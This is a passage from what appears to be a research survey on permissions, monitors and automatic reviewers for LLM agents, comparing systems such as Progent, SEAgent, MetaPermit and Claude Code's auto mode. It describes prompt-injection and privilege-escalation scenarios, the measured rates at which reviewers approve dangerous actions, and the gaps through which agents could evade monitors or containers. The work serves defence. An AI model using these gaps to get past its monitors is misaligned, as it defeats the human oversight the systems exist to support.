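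Researchers tested 119 OAuth servers and found 325 flaws. Nearly all the servers had a flaw in dynamic registration, which lets an unknown program register itself as a client. On 81 of these servers, a user could also link an account at another service, such as GitHub. If such a server wrongly identifies someone else as the user, it becomes a confused deputy, acting for that person with the user's authority at the other service. Every tested server had a flaw, but this may not be true of OAuth servers in general, because the researchers had to exclude 316 that were behind strict company access controls.

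*Exposed by Design* (Padilla, July 2026), a smaller study, went further and tested how servers behave. It found that 91.8% of 414 servers did not use OAuth, although some may have used fixed keys. Of the servers Padilla confirmed in one round, 41.6% had disappeared three days later, so a company's list of approved servers can go out of date within a week.

### Blocking beforehand and detecting afterwards

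A monitor that blocks requests has to judge each one before it runs, so it misses anything the request does not show, such as a test tool that also sends its results to a remote service. It also misses harm that an agent does through a permitted operation, and it sometimes blocks legitimate work.

Detection afterwards can use better evidence. A log of network traffic shows where the test results actually went, and a reviewer can examine the whole session instead of one call. By then, however, the private key may be on a public server. Although the developer can replace a leaked key, she cannot recall a leaked document. Logs also record only the permissions that agents have used. As Zhou and Zhang point out, an ordinary run may never use an agent's excess access, so a clean log does not show that the grant was narrow.

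The case for blocking has grown stronger as tools have become more powerful. Acharya and Gupta cite a study of 177,436 MCP tools, which found that the share of tools that change something in the outside world rose from 27% to 65% between November 2024 and February 2026. Detection still matters for agents that may misbehave without an attacker. Google DeepMind's plan for controlling AI, as Wei and Xiong describe it, treats a possibly misaligned agent as an insider threat and sets the level of detection and response according to the model's abilities.

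### Where a monitor can stand

A push passes through several layers of software, and a monitor at each layer sees a different description of it.

| Position | What the monitor sees | What it can miss |
|---|---|---|
| Tool gateway, between the agent and its tools | The tool's name and the details of the call | What the tool does next, and any tool that bypasses the gateway |
| Application, such as the repository server | The branch, its owner and the changed files | Everything the agent does in other applications |
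| Browser, if the agent works through web pages | The page and the requests it sends | Programs outside the browser |
| Operating system | The files and processes involved | Whether a commit is the fix or a stolen key |
| Network | The destination and the amount of data | Encrypted contents, and the purpose of the transfer |

*Progent* (Shi, He and colleagues, 2025) works at the tool gateway. Its policies are rules that allow or forbid a tool depending on the details of the call, such as "Slack messages only to Alice". Forbidding rules take precedence, and the monitor refuses any call that no rule allows. It returns the reason to the agent, so the agent can look for another way to finish the task.

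A language model writes the first set of rules from the user's request and proposes changes as results arrive. A solver then checks whether the new rules allow any call that the old ones blocked. If they do, someone must approve the change; otherwise it takes effect at once. On AgentDojo, only 6% of changes needed approval.

On AgentDojo, 39.9% of attacks on GPT-4o agents succeeded without Progent and 1.0% succeeded with it. On Agent Security Bench, Progent lowered the success rate from 70.3% to 3.9%. In these runs the software approved every expansion automatically, so the figures measure how well a language model writes rules, and the solver's check added nothing to them. On AgentDojo, the first set of rules alone reduced the rate to 2.5%, and human review reduced it to zero.

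Progent also lets an organisation set standing rules, which the monitor checks before the task's rules. Shi and colleagues state that the combination never allows more than the standing rules do, but their algorithm guarantees this only for calls that the standing rules explicitly forbid. If the standing rules don't cover a call, the monitor applies the task's rules, which may allow it, even though a meet of the two policies would refuse it.

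The monitor's coverage depends on how it is installed. Developers can build Progent into an agent and cover all its tools. Users can instead route the agent's outside connections through Progent without changing the agent, but Progent then doesn't check the agent's built-in tools.

A rule about the details of a call may also fail to account for what those details mean. For example, a gateway may not treat 15 October as part of October. *AC4A* (Sharma and Grossman, 2026) has each application describe its resources as a tree, in which a year contains months and a month contains days. When an agent calls the application or uses its web page, the application determines which resources the agent needs. The monitor subtracts the resources covered by the agent's permissions from those it needs and allows the operation if none remain.

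Suppose the agent needs to read the calendar for 9 and 10 October and has a separate permission for each day. Subtracting the first permission from the request leaves 10 October, and subtracting the second leaves nothing, so the monitor allows the call. A monitor that looked for a single permission covering both days would have refused it.

The subtraction is safe only if it never drops a resource the agent still lacks. Sharma and Grossman instead require that the remainder contain nothing outside the original need. This condition is not enough, because a faulty function that always returned an empty remainder would meet it and allow everything. They demonstrate AC4A on a game of tic-tac-toe and a flight booking involving a calendar, a travel site and a payment wallet, so there is no attack rate to compare with Progent's.

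AC4A depends on applications to describe their own resources. ceLLMate, another system in Zhou and Zhang's survey, intercepts the browser's requests and maps them to actions such as making a purchase, so its protection depends on that mapping being correct.

*AgentBound* (Bühler, Biagiola and colleagues, 2025) limits what a tool server can reach through the operating system and the network. Each server has a manifest that lists the kinds of access it needs, and the user fills in the particular folders and addresses. The server then runs in a container, an isolated environment where it can open only those folders and contact only those addresses. This requires no changes to the server's code.

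In one test of AgentBound, a malicious server tried to steal a private key. When AgentBound blocked its network access, the server could read the key but not send it. Limiting its file access as well prevented it from reading the key. AgentBound also stopped a Google Maps server that secretly switched to another address. It did not stop a poisoned tool description with instructions to redirect cryptocurrency transfers, because the attack changed only the details of a permitted request.

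Bühler and colleagues used language models to write manifests for 296 popular servers and report that 80.9% were correct. That figure is based on only 25 responses from developers, who were sent 96 of the manifests. Seventeen accepted the manifest, four rejected it and four were still discussing it. In a separate check on 48 servers, the manifests agreed with human-written ones on 96.5% of entries. Most of the errors were missing permissions, which would break the server rather than give it too much access.

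The container added 0.6 milliseconds to an average operation on a Mac and 0.29 on Linux. Starting a server took up to about 0.4 seconds longer.

### The shell

A shell runs whatever command it receives, including commands that read files, fetch web pages, push code and start other programs, so permission to use it can cover most other permissions. A product lattice doesn't capture this overlap because it treats each permission as independent. For example, a grant that sets reading to "never" and the shell to "always" is incomparable in the lattice with a grant that allows only reading. In practice, the first grant gives the agent more authority, because the agent can read any file with the command `cat`.

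Bühler and colleagues came across this when they described their 296 servers using Android's permissions. A few servers that seemed to need a phone's camera, text messages or location actually controlled a connected phone through a command-line program, so in AgentBound's own vocabulary they needed only permission to execute commands. Only a small minority of the 296 servers needed that permission, but Padilla counted 687 tools on public servers that offered a shell without access controls.

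Checking the text of each command helps less than it seems to. Suppose the developer allows only the command that runs her tests. Test files are programs, and the agent has permission to edit them, so it can write a test that sends her private key to a stranger and then run the permitted command. The check doesn't catch this because the text of the command hasn't changed.

A monitor in the operating system can enforce limits without interpreting the command. If the shell runs in a container that holds only the project folder and has no network connection, the malicious test cannot find a key or send one anywhere. The shell's effective authority is then the meet of what its commands could do and what the container allows. The agent can still ruin the project folder, and pushing has to go through a separate tool outside the container. An agent could also escape by exploiting a flaw in the container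 software or the system kernel.

In *AeonBox*, Fonseca proposes removing the shell. The agent instead writes a short program that can call only a fixed set of GitHub operations, and a type checker examines the whole program before any of it runs. For example, the checker rejects a program that reads a private repository and then opens a public issue. Checking first prevents a forbidden plan from being partly carried out. Fonseca has published no measurements. The approach would also restrict the developer's agent, which could run her tests only if someone had written a checked operation for that.

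### SEAgent's model of escalation

The monitors described so far mostly judge one call at a time. SEAgent, from January 2026, looks at the route by which information reached the call. Ji, Wu and colleagues (2026), in *Taming Various Privilege Escalation in LLM-Based Agent Systems*, begin with a formal model of users, agents, tools and databases. An agent *a* is a function:

(*Tₐ*, *rₐ*) = agentₐ(*cₐ*, *Eₐ*)

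Here *cₐ* is the agent's context (what it has seen so far), and *Eₐ* is the set of new inputs. The agent returns a set of actions *Tₐ* (tool calls or messages to other agents) and a written reply *rₐ*. A round starts with a user's request *q* and ends when no agent proposes another action.

Let *T_q* be the smallest set of actions that fulfils the request. An agent escalates if it takes any action outside *T_q*. This definition is stricter than checking whether the agent exceeded its grant, because opening one unnecessary file counts as escalation even if the user permits it. It is also hard to apply, because nobody has a list of the necessary actions in advance and two different plans may both fulfil the request without unnecessary actions. Ji and colleagues acknowledge the first difficulty, and SEAgent looks for suspicious routes instead of computing *T_q*.

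In the model, an attacker could act through five kinds of event, each of which gives one escalation scenario. Most of the examples come from a smart home.

| Event | Scenario | Example |
|---|---|---|
| A user makes a request | Direct prompt injection | A guest's text, joined to the owner's request, orders the agent to open the front door |
| A tool returns a result | Indirect prompt injection | The owner asks the agent to admit her daughter, and a guest's message supplies the guest's ID instead |
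| A database returns text | Database poisoning | Planted text tells the agent to open the door |
| One agent messages another | Confused deputy | A search agent asks the smart-lock agent to unlock the door |
| A third-party agent calls a tool | Untrusted agent | An agent with hidden instructions calls a sensitive tool itself |

The researchers carried out the first four kinds of attack against existing systems. The second kind got past CaMeL, which fixes the order of steps in advance but let the ID come from the attacker's message.

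Ji and colleagues assume that agents escalate only when an attacker prompts them. Their threat model therefore leaves out the overeager coding agents that deleted files during harmless tasks.

### Following information to the tool

During each round, SEAgent builds a graph whose points are the users, agents, tools and databases involved. It adds an arrow whenever information passes from one to another. When the search agent persuades its neighbour to unlock the door, the graph contains this route:

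search agent → smart-lock agent → unlock tool

SEAgent also gives each participant fixed labels. A tool's labels record whether it acts on something local, external or physical; whether it reads, writes or executes; how sensitive the operation is; whether its results are trusted; and whether they are personal. Agents are labeled for trust, and databases for trust and privacy. A language model proposes the labels and people correct them.

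A policy combines a route with conditions on the labels, and tells the monitor to allow, refuse or ask. Ji and colleagues tested four policies, all of which refuse:

| Information comes from | It may not lead, by any route, to |
|---|---|
| An external tool with untrusted results | A tool that writes or executes, at moderate or high sensitivity |
| A highly sensitive tool that returns personal data | The email tool |
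| An untrusted database | Any tool above low sensitivity |
| An untrusted agent | Any tool above low sensitivity |

The last policy blocks the unlock tool because the request's route began at an untrusted agent, even though the trusted smart-lock agent sent the request. For direct prompt injection, SEAgent relies on keeping each user's context and memory separate.

If the developer's agent read online documentation and then pushed code, the first policy would refuse the push, whether the agent was publishing the fix or the private key. But if it read the key and pushed without having used the web, no policy would apply, because the second one covers only email. SEAgent allows any operation that matches no policy, so a forgotten policy leaves a gap for an attacker. Progent refuses any call that matches no rule, so an omission there interrupts legitimate work instead.

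SEAgent clears both the graph and the agents' contexts after each round. If it cleared only the graph, an instruction planted in the first round could influence the agents in the second with no record of its source. SEAgent keeps past requests and tool results, along with their sources, in a separate memory. When the next round needs an old result, SEAgent restores both the text and its place in the graph.

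### What SEAgent's results support

The researchers compared SEAgent with an unprotected agent and with IsolateGPT, an earlier system that isolates an agent's applications from one another. The table gives the share of attacks that succeeded, with ranges across types of harm.

| Attacks | Unprotected | IsolateGPT | SEAgent |
|---|---|---|---|
| AgentDojo | 39.1% | 0.8% | 0% |
| InjecAgent, through tool results | 7.2% to 46.1% | 0% | 0% |
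| InjecAgent, through a poisoned database | 49.7% to 80.0% | 3.3% to 54.6% | 0% |

The zeros depend on correct labels, and the policies target these kinds of attack. For confused deputies and untrusted agents, the evidence is one worked example with the smart lock, because no large benchmark existed.

Ji and colleagues measured interference with legitimate tasks on a different benchmark, API-Bank. SEAgent wrongly blocked none of the tasks that used one or two tools and 5.13% of those that used three or more. IsolateGPT wrongly blocked 5.3% to 18.3%. The share of correct tool calls ranged from eight percentage points below the unprotected agent's to four above it.

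Two tasks account for SEAgent's 5.13% false alarm rate. In both, the agent consulted Wikipedia, whose results were labelled untrusted, and then tried to record health data or book an appointment. Ji and colleagues suggest labelling Wikipedia as trusted. That would remove the false alarms, but because anyone can edit Wikipedia, it would also give attackers a route to the same tools.

The low rate of false alarms may not carry over to AgentDojo, where many legitimate tasks require outside text to influence an action. The label-based systems failed a large share of those tasks, and SEAgent's first policy forbids many of the same flows. The two sets of results therefore do not show that SEAgent can block every attack and still allow legitimate work on the same tasks.

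Checking the policies took three to six milliseconds on average. The memory had a larger effect, raising the amount of text the models processed by about a third on API-Bank's short conversations. The average share of correct calls there was 68.3%, against 73.0% for the unprotected agent. In longer tasks with several agents, the memory reduced the amount of text by 32% to 39%. The agents also met more of their goals in those tasks, but the researchers had switched the policies off because the tools were simulated, so the improvement doesn't measure how enforcement affects performance.

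### How a correct policy becomes a broad permission

An escalation can get through even when every check works as designed. In the earlier example, the policy "send summary *S* to Alice" became a token that grants only "may send mail", so the mail service will accept the token even if the agent sends the summary to Bob.

Zhou and Zhang state the condition that a faithful implementation must meet. Let *P* be the approved policy and *M*(*P*) the tokens and rules that implement it. Let *E*(*M*(*P*)) be the effects those controls allow, and let α restate these effects in the policy's own terms. Then:

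α(*E*(*M*(*P*))) ⊆ ⟦*P*⟧

The right-hand side is the set of effects that the policy allows, here only "*S* goes to Alice". The left-hand side also contains "*S* goes to Bob" and "the private key goes to Alice", so the condition fails. The condition excludes forbidden effects but doesn't require the allowed ones, so a useless mail service that delivered nothing would satisfy it.

Wei and Xiong prove that a translation which keeps the permitted actions but drops restrictions can only enlarge what a policy allows. They also show that a chain of monitors allows only the requests that every monitor allows. Losing restrictions at the mail service is therefore harmless if a tool gateway has already checked the recipient and the content. This works only if the agent cannot bypass the gateway. An agent with the mail token and a shell could contact the mail service directly, so the gateway should keep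 the token and send the mail itself.

### Contracts for a tool's effects

To apply the condition, a monitor has to know what each tool call can do. Zhou and Zhang propose effect contracts, which list the resources an operation may read, the data it may send, the possible recipients and the changes it may make elsewhere. Wei and Xiong turn this into a test. For a call *c*, let κ(*c*) be the effects listed in the contract and *C* the effects the grant permits. The monitor allows the call only if κ(*c*) ⊆ *C*. If the contract lists every effect the call can have, then:

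actual effects of *c* ⊆ κ(*c*) ⊆ *C*

So no effect exceeds the grant, as long as every effect passes through a monitor that applies this test.

A useful contract depends on the details of the call. For mail to Bob, it would list "*S* goes to Bob", which is outside the grant, so the monitor refuses the call. For mail to Alice, it would list only the permitted effect. If the most specific contract the mail service can provide is "this operation may send anything to anyone", the monitor has to refuse both calls. An accurate contract for a shell command would be almost as broad, unless a container limits what the command can do.

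An overcautious contract blocks legitimate work, which someone will probably notice. An incomplete contract is more dangerous because the monitor keeps approving calls with effects the contract omits. A tool that was safe last month may now forward data, so each contract has to specify a version of the tool. Zhou and Zhang suggest building contracts from program analysis, sandbox trial runs, network records and developers' descriptions. Contracts for remotely hosted services remain difficult to build because outsiders cannot inspect the services' code.

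Detection after the fact can help fix a tool's contract. If network records show a test tool contacting an address that its contract omits, the monitor has been approving calls based on false information. Wei and Xiong would then revoke the contract, which blocks every later call to that tool until someone describes its effects again. They have specified this system and proved its properties, but have not yet measured it in use.

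## Setting a grant and asking for more

A monitor can enforce a grant exactly, but someone still has to choose the grant. The lattice helps little with that choice, because it orders {read} below {read, push} but doesn't determine which of the two the developer's agent needs.

### Choosing a plan before choosing permissions

Suppose an assistant must prepare a report from approved records. It can process them locally or use a hosted service, but the hosted option also draws on a wider dataset.

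| Permission | Local plan | Hosted plan |
|---|---|---|
| Read the approved records | Needed | Needed |
| Read the wider dataset | Not needed | Needed |
| Send data to the analysis service | Not needed | Needed |

Even the smallest grant that makes the hosted plan work is too large if the local plan produces an equally good report.

Zhou and Zhang would have the agent look first for a plan that fits the permissions it already has. Let Π*q*(*g*) be the set of plans that achieve the goal *g* to at least the quality *q*, let *A*(π) be the permissions that plan π requires, and let *G* be the current grant. The agent looks for a plan such that:

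π ∈ Π*q*(*g*) and *A*(π) ⊆ *G*

If *G* allows only reading the approved records, the local plan qualifies and the hosted one does not. If several plans qualify, the choice depends on each plan's cost and how much access, disclosure and user effort it requires. If none qualifies, the agent can request a specific addition to the grant, offer a more modest result or ask the user what she meant.

Some plans are incomparable. One may need sensitive local files, while another sends less sensitive data to an outside company. Zhou and Zhang suggest presenting such plans together, with the permissions each needs.

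MiniScope, a permission system for agents, starts one step later, after the agent has proposed a plan. *How Agents Ask for Permission* (Michael and Roesner, 2026) explains that MiniScope finds the smallest set of permissions the plan needs by using integer linear programming, a method for finding the best combination of whole-number choices. Given the hosted plan, it would correctly select all three permissions in the table. The result also depends on how finely a service divides its permissions. If a mail service combines reading and sending in a single permission, an agent that needs to read must also receive the right to send.

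### Permission modes in coding agents

Most users of coding agents choose a ready-made mode instead of writing a grant. Anthropic's *Permission modes* describes six for Claude Code.

| Mode | What runs without asking the user | What happens to other actions |
|---|---|---|
| Plan | Reading and exploring | Edits wait until the user approves a plan |
| Manual | Mostly reading | The user decides |
| Accept edits | Also file edits and common file commands in the project folder | The user decides |
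| Auto | Reading, edits in the project folder, and actions that a second model approves | The software blocks them and tells the agent why |
| Don't ask | What Manual mode allows, plus actions approved in advance | The software refuses them |
| Bypass permissions | Nearly everything | A few dangerous actions still need an answer |

The modes do not form a chain, because neither "accept edits" nor auto mode is a stricter version of the other. "Accept edits" lets the agent delete an old file in the project folder without asking, while auto mode by default blocks the agent from irreversibly destroying files that existed before the session. But auto mode can approve a web request that would need the user's approval under "accept edits".

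OpenAI's Codex sets what the agent can reach separately from whom it must ask to go further, while Claude Code's modes partly combine the two. According to OpenAI's *Agent approvals & security*, the operating system by default denies Codex network access and lets it write only in the active workspace. One setting controls whether Codex may ask to go beyond those limits, and another controls whether the user or a reviewing agent answers. "Full access" removes both the sandbox limits and the approval requests.

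The cloud version of Codex also changes permissions between phases. During setup, it can use the network and stored secrets to install what the project needs. It then removes the secrets, and the agent works offline unless the user has allowed internet access.

Fixed modes do not take the particular job into account. Michael and Roesner give the example of a product that sends passport details only to recognised airlines. This rule is too strict for a customer of a small specialist travel agency, and too loose for someone who never wants an agent to share her passport. *Towards Automating Data Access Permissions in AI Agents* (2025) makes a related point about phones, contrasting permissions granted at installation with those granted during use. Granting them at installation assumes that people know in advance what an app will need, whereas an agent often finds out what it needs while it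 works.

### Rules that administrators write

An organisation can stop its employees from making some of these choices. OpenAI's *Running Codex safely* describes an administrator's file that allows only the read-only and workspace-write sandboxes, so an employee cannot select full access. OpenAI also lets Codex reach expected network destinations, blocks some others and requires approval for unfamiliar ones.

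The location of a rule matters as well as its content. Claude Code ignores a setting in a project's files that would start a session in auto or bypass mode, because otherwise whoever wrote a downloaded project could widen the permissions of the agent that opened it. Administrators can also write rules that forbid particular tools or commands in every mode.

In *The Agent Access Model*, published by the network company Cloudflare, Silverlock proposes that a company write one template for each kind of task and reuse it every time the task runs. For example, a template for reconciling accounts might allow an agent to read three tables and post to one channel. When a task starts, the system keeps only the permissions shared by the template, the agent service and the person who started the task, then applies the resource owner's policy. It refuses everything the result does not list.

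Someone still has to write the templates, and few organisations treat this as a priority. Zorz (2026), in *AI agent permissions are outrunning security*, reports a survey of 1,100 IT and security decision-makers:

- 70% said they let AI take actions that would have required human approval a year earlier.
- 84% said they could see how AI systems access data, but only 49% could see and audit every action an agent takes.
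- About a quarter named defining an agent's permissions as one of their two main controls, which made it the least popular choice.

Most respondents nevertheless agreed that limiting what AI can access matters more than predicting every threat. Raghu Nandakumara of the security company Illumio told Zorz that defining a new agent's permissions is hard and that nobody wants to disrupt the workflow that made it useful. He said organisations intend to add limits once they understand the agent better, but "that day rarely comes".

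### Conseca writes a policy for each task

*Contextual Agent Security* (Tsai and Bagdasarian, 2025) describes Conseca, a system built at Google in which a language model writes the rules. The model receives the user's request, descriptions of the tools and whatever context the developer has chosen to trust, such as folder names. It writes a policy before the agent starts work, and ordinary code then checks each action against that policy. The model that writes the policy never sees the contents of emails or web pages, so an attacker cannot use them to influence the rules.

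In one example, Alice asks her agent to answer urgent work emails. Conseca lets the agent send mail only from Alice's account, to addresses at her company, with "urgent" in the subject line, and it forbids deleting mail. It also gives a reason for each rule so that a person can check the rule before the agent starts. The model's subject-line rule is a guess at which emails are urgent, and it would block a reply to an urgent message that did not use the word.

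Tsai and Bagdasarian compared Conseca with two fixed policies on 20 office tasks that they had designed.

| Policy | Tasks completed, average of five runs | Did it block an inappropriate forwarding request? |
|---|---|---|
| None | 14.0 | No |
| Fixed: allow everything except deletion | 12.2 | No |
| Fixed: forbid every change | 0.0 | Yes |
| Conseca | 12.0 | Yes |

For the last column, the researchers planted an email asking the agent to forward messages about security flaws. Conseca blocked the forwarding except when the user had told the agent to perform the tasks in her urgent emails. The result shows why a policy should depend on the task, but one planted request is weak evidence about attacks in general.

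The isolation that protects Conseca also limits it. If Alice asks the agent to do the tasks in her manager's email, the policy's author cannot read that email to learn which permissions the tasks need. The model may also misunderstand what Alice wants. *Extending the Formalism and Theoretical Foundations of Cryptography to AI* (2026) adds that an attacker who has taken over the agent could predict the policy and reach a forbidden result through a series of permitted actions. A policy written for one task therefore still needs checks on combinations of actions.

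### MetaPermit asks five questions about each call

Ma, Hariri and colleagues (2026), in *MetaPermit*, let the model describe a tool call but not write the rules or decide whether to allow it. Before each call, the model answers five questions by choosing from fixed lists:

| Question | Possible answers |
|---|---|
| Does the user want an action or only a conversation? | Action, conversation |
| Is the user's goal clear? | Clear, ambiguous, incomprehensible |
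| Could the action cause irreversible harm or disclose private data? | High risk, low risk |
| Does the tool serve the goal? | Directly, as a preliminary step, in support, no |
| Does the request justify the details of the call? | Yes, no |

Fixed rules turn the answers into a decision. The answers have only 96 possible combinations, so an administrator can check the decision for each one.

Suppose Alice asks her agent to refund $1,500 to Bob, and an attacker, Eve, has planted a note in the transaction history telling the agent to pay her instead. Sending money serves Alice's goal, so the monitor allows the payment tool. But nothing in Alice's request justifies using Eve's account number, so the monitor blocks the payment and returns the reason. The agent can then pay Bob.

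Ma and colleagues tested MetaPermit on AgentDojo and AgentDyn, a newer set of open-ended tasks. With the model Qwen3-235B, attack success fell from 26.49% to zero, and the share of user tasks completed under attack fell from 62.37% to 50.13%. With MiniMax-M2.7, attack success fell from 2.85% to 0.08%, and the share of tasks completed fell from 62.77% to 53.92%. No malicious call ran in any of the attacks counted as successes in that 0.08%.

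With MetaPermit, the share of tasks MiniMax completed fell from 72.0% to 69.4% on AgentDojo and from 54.45% to 29.67% on AgentDyn's GitHub tasks. The researchers had derived the five questions from AgentDojo's tasks, so AgentDyn is the better test of how the method handles tasks they had not anticipated.

They also gave the model 95 malicious calls together with text that revealed the rules and told it which answers to choose. The text led the model to lower its risk estimate in 16.8% of cases, but no call passed, because the other answers still blocked it.

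Even fixed rules give varying decisions when the answers vary. Ma and colleagues ran each of 50 queries 20 times. MetaPermit reached the same decision every time on 42% of the queries, compared with 32% when the same model just answered "allow" or "deny". MetaPermit also decides call by call, so a user cannot review the whole grant in advance as she could with Conseca.

### Approval fatigue

A system can ask the user what she wants instead of predicting it, but the drawback is that it has to ask often. Anthropic's *How we built Claude Code auto mode* reports that users accepted 93% of permission prompts, and its *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (2026) gives a later figure of 97%.

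Most permission requests are probably harmless, so a high approval rate does not prove that people have stopped reading them. An experiment commissioned by Anthropic gives better evidence. A research company paid 1,053 professional testers to take part in a coding study, and partway through each session the software replaced one permission prompt with a request to run an obviously dangerous command. 143 testers (13.6%) refused it. The refusal rate was about 17% when the command appeared early in a session and about 5% when it appeared after 50 or more prompts.

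The testers worked in a temporary environment and had no code of their own to lose, which may have made them less careful than ordinary users. These conditions don't explain the decline during a session as easily, since it appeared among people who were all working under them.

People appear to pay more attention to larger decisions. Claude Code users reject 39% of the plans the agent presents, compared with 3% of individual permission requests. Some of the plan rejections must concern how to write the code rather than what the agent may access. Still, a plan gives the user a chance to object to the hosted service before the agent asks for each permission it needs.

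Frequent prompts also lead users to approve too much in advance. According to Anthropic, 62% of users have used bypass mode or chosen "don't ask again" for shell commands, and a quarter of interactive sessions start in bypass mode. Many users have approved every command that starts with `python`, which lets the agent run any Python program it can write. OpenAI found the same rule among its own employees, along with one configuration file that always allowed Codex to start an unrestricted copy of itself.

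### Automatic reviewers and their errors

Both companies now offer a second model that answers these requests in the user's place. Anthropic made its version, auto mode, the default on individual and team plans in August 2026. OpenAI's *Auto-review of agent actions without synchronous human oversight* (Trębacz, Arnesen and colleagues, 2026) illustrates how far a reviewer can reduce interruptions. Of 10,000 actions in Codex, 9,280 stayed inside the sandbox and needed no review. The reviewer approved 713 of the other 720 and refused seven. Codex found another way to continue after four of the refusals and stopped to ask the user after the other three.

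The developers have also measured how often their reviewers approve something they should block.

| Reviewer and test | Dangerous actions approved | Measured by |
|---|---|---|
| Claude Code, 52 real overeager actions | 17% | Anthropic |
| Claude Code, 1,000 artificial data thefts | 5.7% | Anthropic |
| Claude Code, the commands shown to the paid testers | 11% | Anthropic |
| Codex, artificial overeager actions | 9.7% | Trębacz and colleagues |
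| Codex, artificial prompt injections | 0.7% | Trębacz and colleagues |

The tests use different actions, so their results don't show which product is better. The 17% comes from testing an earlier version of auto mode on only 52 actions, but those actions came from real work. In the same evaluation, the reviewer wrongly blocked 0.4% of ordinary calls.

When the reviewer missed a real overeager action, it had usually recognised the danger but wrongly concluded that the user had consented. For example, a user who says "clean up the PR" has asked for changes to a pull request but has not agreed to let the agent overwrite the project's history. Anthropic's engineers tried different instructions to correct this, but none helped more than it harmed.

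Ambiguous requests make the problem much worse. In *Measuring the Permission Gate*, Ji, Li and colleagues (2026) independently tested auto mode on 128 ambiguous requests and found that it missed 81.0% of the actions it should have stopped. This fits the earlier finding that automatic checkers often approve out-of-scope actions when the user has not stated the scope, though the rate does not describe ordinary use.

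In the newest prompt injection tests, Trajectory Labs, which Anthropic hired to test auto mode, made 720 attempts against each of three recent Claude models. None succeeded with the permission checks on, but an average of only 0.09% succeeded with them off, so the results are stronger evidence of the agents' own resistance than of their reviewers' effectiveness.

An automatic reviewer can also make it less clear who is deciding. Michael and Roesner tried five commercial agents in May and June 2026. With Claude's chatbot set to "Needs approval", a model sometimes approved an action without telling the user. ChatGPT prompted the user about every action covered by a permission setting, but in its agent mode, which controls a remote browser, the researchers found no way to set permissions.

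Trębacz and colleagues warn that their reviewer sees only requests to leave the sandbox. A model hiding its intentions could describe such a request as harmless, or do damage inside the sandbox.

### What an agent reads may not widen its grant

Suppose a grant allows an agent to send a summary to a partner company's contact. A trusted directory lists Alice as the contact, but a document the agent retrieves contains an instruction to copy the message to Bob. Zhou and Zhang distinguish between using the directory to identify the recipient, whom the grant did not name, and following the document's instruction, which would disclose the summary to someone the grant does not allow.

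The agent may accept a restriction from any source, because a meet never enlarges a grant. Adding a recipient does enlarge it, so if documents could add recipients, anyone able to show the agent a document could choose the agent's permissions. The directory must still be trustworthy, because an attacker who could edit it could redirect the summary to any recipient the grant allows.

A source can still be dangerous when it is restricted to yes-or-no answers, as FIDES can do. If the question is whether a confidential draft has approval for release, a single "yes" can release it, so the system must check that the source has the authority to make that decision.

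A user can give such authority in advance. For example, she might let the agent follow instructions in her manager's task list, as long as the instructions stay within a fixed set of actions. Progent applies the same principle to changes that nobody authorised beforehand by requiring a person to approve any expansion.

Auto mode follows part of this rule by hiding information from its reviewer. Claude Code sends the reviewer the user's messages and the agent's proposed actions, but not the results of tool calls or the agent's explanations. Text on a malicious web page therefore cannot reach the reviewer directly, and the agent cannot persuade the reviewer to approve an action. But the reviewer also loses useful evidence. If the agent proposes canceling job 123, the reviewer cannot tell whether the number came from a search or the agent made it up.

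Claude Code also makes it easier for a user to narrow permissions than to widen them. If she writes "don't push", the reviewer blocks pushes until she lifts the restriction. Writing "you can force-push" doesn't unblock a force push, because she hasn't named the branch the agent may overwrite. An approval normally covers one action. But a restriction can disappear when the software shortens a long conversation and removes the message containing it, so Anthropic recommends a written rule for anything that must always hold.

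### Wider scopes and shorter grants

An agent sometimes needs more permission than it has. In MCP, a server can respond to a request with a scope challenge, which indicates that the agent's token does not cover the operation. The agent's software can then seek a token with a wider scope, which is called step-up authorization. Silverlock points out that MCP's authorization rules apply to connections over HTTP and do not limit individual tools or the details of a call. The software around the agent or the tool server has to enforce those limits.

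A server that requests a wider scope also has no authority to grant one. In Silverlock's design, a scope challenge can obtain only permissions within the task's original limit. If the work needs more, someone has to authorise a new task. Logs may show that a template is too narrow, but a policy owner must approve the change, and it applies only to later tasks. Repeated refusals alone do not justify a change, because an attacker can repeat a forbidden request.

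Short-lived grants reduce the access an agent keeps after its work is done. Silverlock's credentials expire no later than the end of the task and work only with a key that the agent's software holds, so someone who steals only the credential cannot use it. Claude Code can grant network access for an even shorter time, to a single sandboxed command. The agent names the sites the command needs, and if the reviewer approves, only that command may contact them.

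An agent may need to search for information before it can say which permissions a job requires. Zhou and Zhang suggest granting permission in stages. The user first allows a limited search, the agent uses the results to look for a plan within its current grant, and it asks for more permissions only if no such plan exists. One approval could then cover several related calls, as long as the approval's conditions still hold.

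Users also need a way to take back what they have granted. Of the 21 research systems that Michael and Roesner examined, only six clearly let users change or revoke permissions later, and two of those allowed changes only between sessions. Commercial agents generally did better, but Claude Cowork, Anthropic's desktop agent, kept a folder permission in any old session that the user reopened. The researchers found no way to remove it permanently except through the operating system's controls, where available, or by uninstalling the app.

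## A ceiling the agent cannot raise: the argument and its premises

A permission that outlives its task may end up held by an agent the user never assessed. In one long session, the developer's agent might save a note to its memory, load a new tool, switch to a newer model, and go from testing code to deploying it. She did not anticipate any of this when she gave her approval that morning. Zhang and Zhang separate three questions: whether the old permission is still valid, how much of it should be in force now, and what the agent may never do under it.

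### How the fixed ceiling works

A grant in their model fixes three things when the user issues it:

- the ceiling *B*, the set of all effects the agent can ever produce under the grant
- the starting authority *P*₀, which lies inside *B*
- the transition envelope, a list of the kinds of change that the grant survives.

During the session, the software around the agent may propose a new active authority, *P′*. The monitor accepts a smaller set at once. It accepts anything else only on evidence that the grant names in advance, such as a passing test run. A proposal that drops one permission and adds another also needs evidence, because the new set is not smaller. In every case the monitor keeps only the part under the ceiling:

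*Pₜ* = *P′* ∩ *B*

Suppose the ceiling lets the agent edit the project, run tests and push to the branch `fix-test`, but the agent starts with permission only to edit and test. When the tests pass, the software proposes letting the agent push to every branch. The monitor activates permission to push to `fix-test` and discards the rest of the proposal. Only a new grant from the developer could let the agent push to the main branch.

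The envelope can end a grant even when every effect stays under the ceiling. If the developer approved an agent that ran on one company's model and the software switches to another company's, the agent may be able to do exactly what it could before, but she has not approved it with the new model. When a change is not on the list, the monitor suspends the grant before the next protected action. Zhang and Zhang sort the changes that matter into six overlapping classes.

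| What changes | Example | Usual response |
|---|---|---|
| The agent's control state | A new model, or a new rule in its memory | Reassess the agent, and continue only if the grant allows this kind of change |
| Its tools | A new credential, or network access | Recompute the active authority |
| Delegation | A new sub-agent | Give the sub-agent a smaller authority, tied to its subtask |
| The phase of the task | From testing to pushing | Use separate authority for each phase |
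| The trust context | Text from a web page becomes a standing instruction | Track the source, and review high-impact actions |
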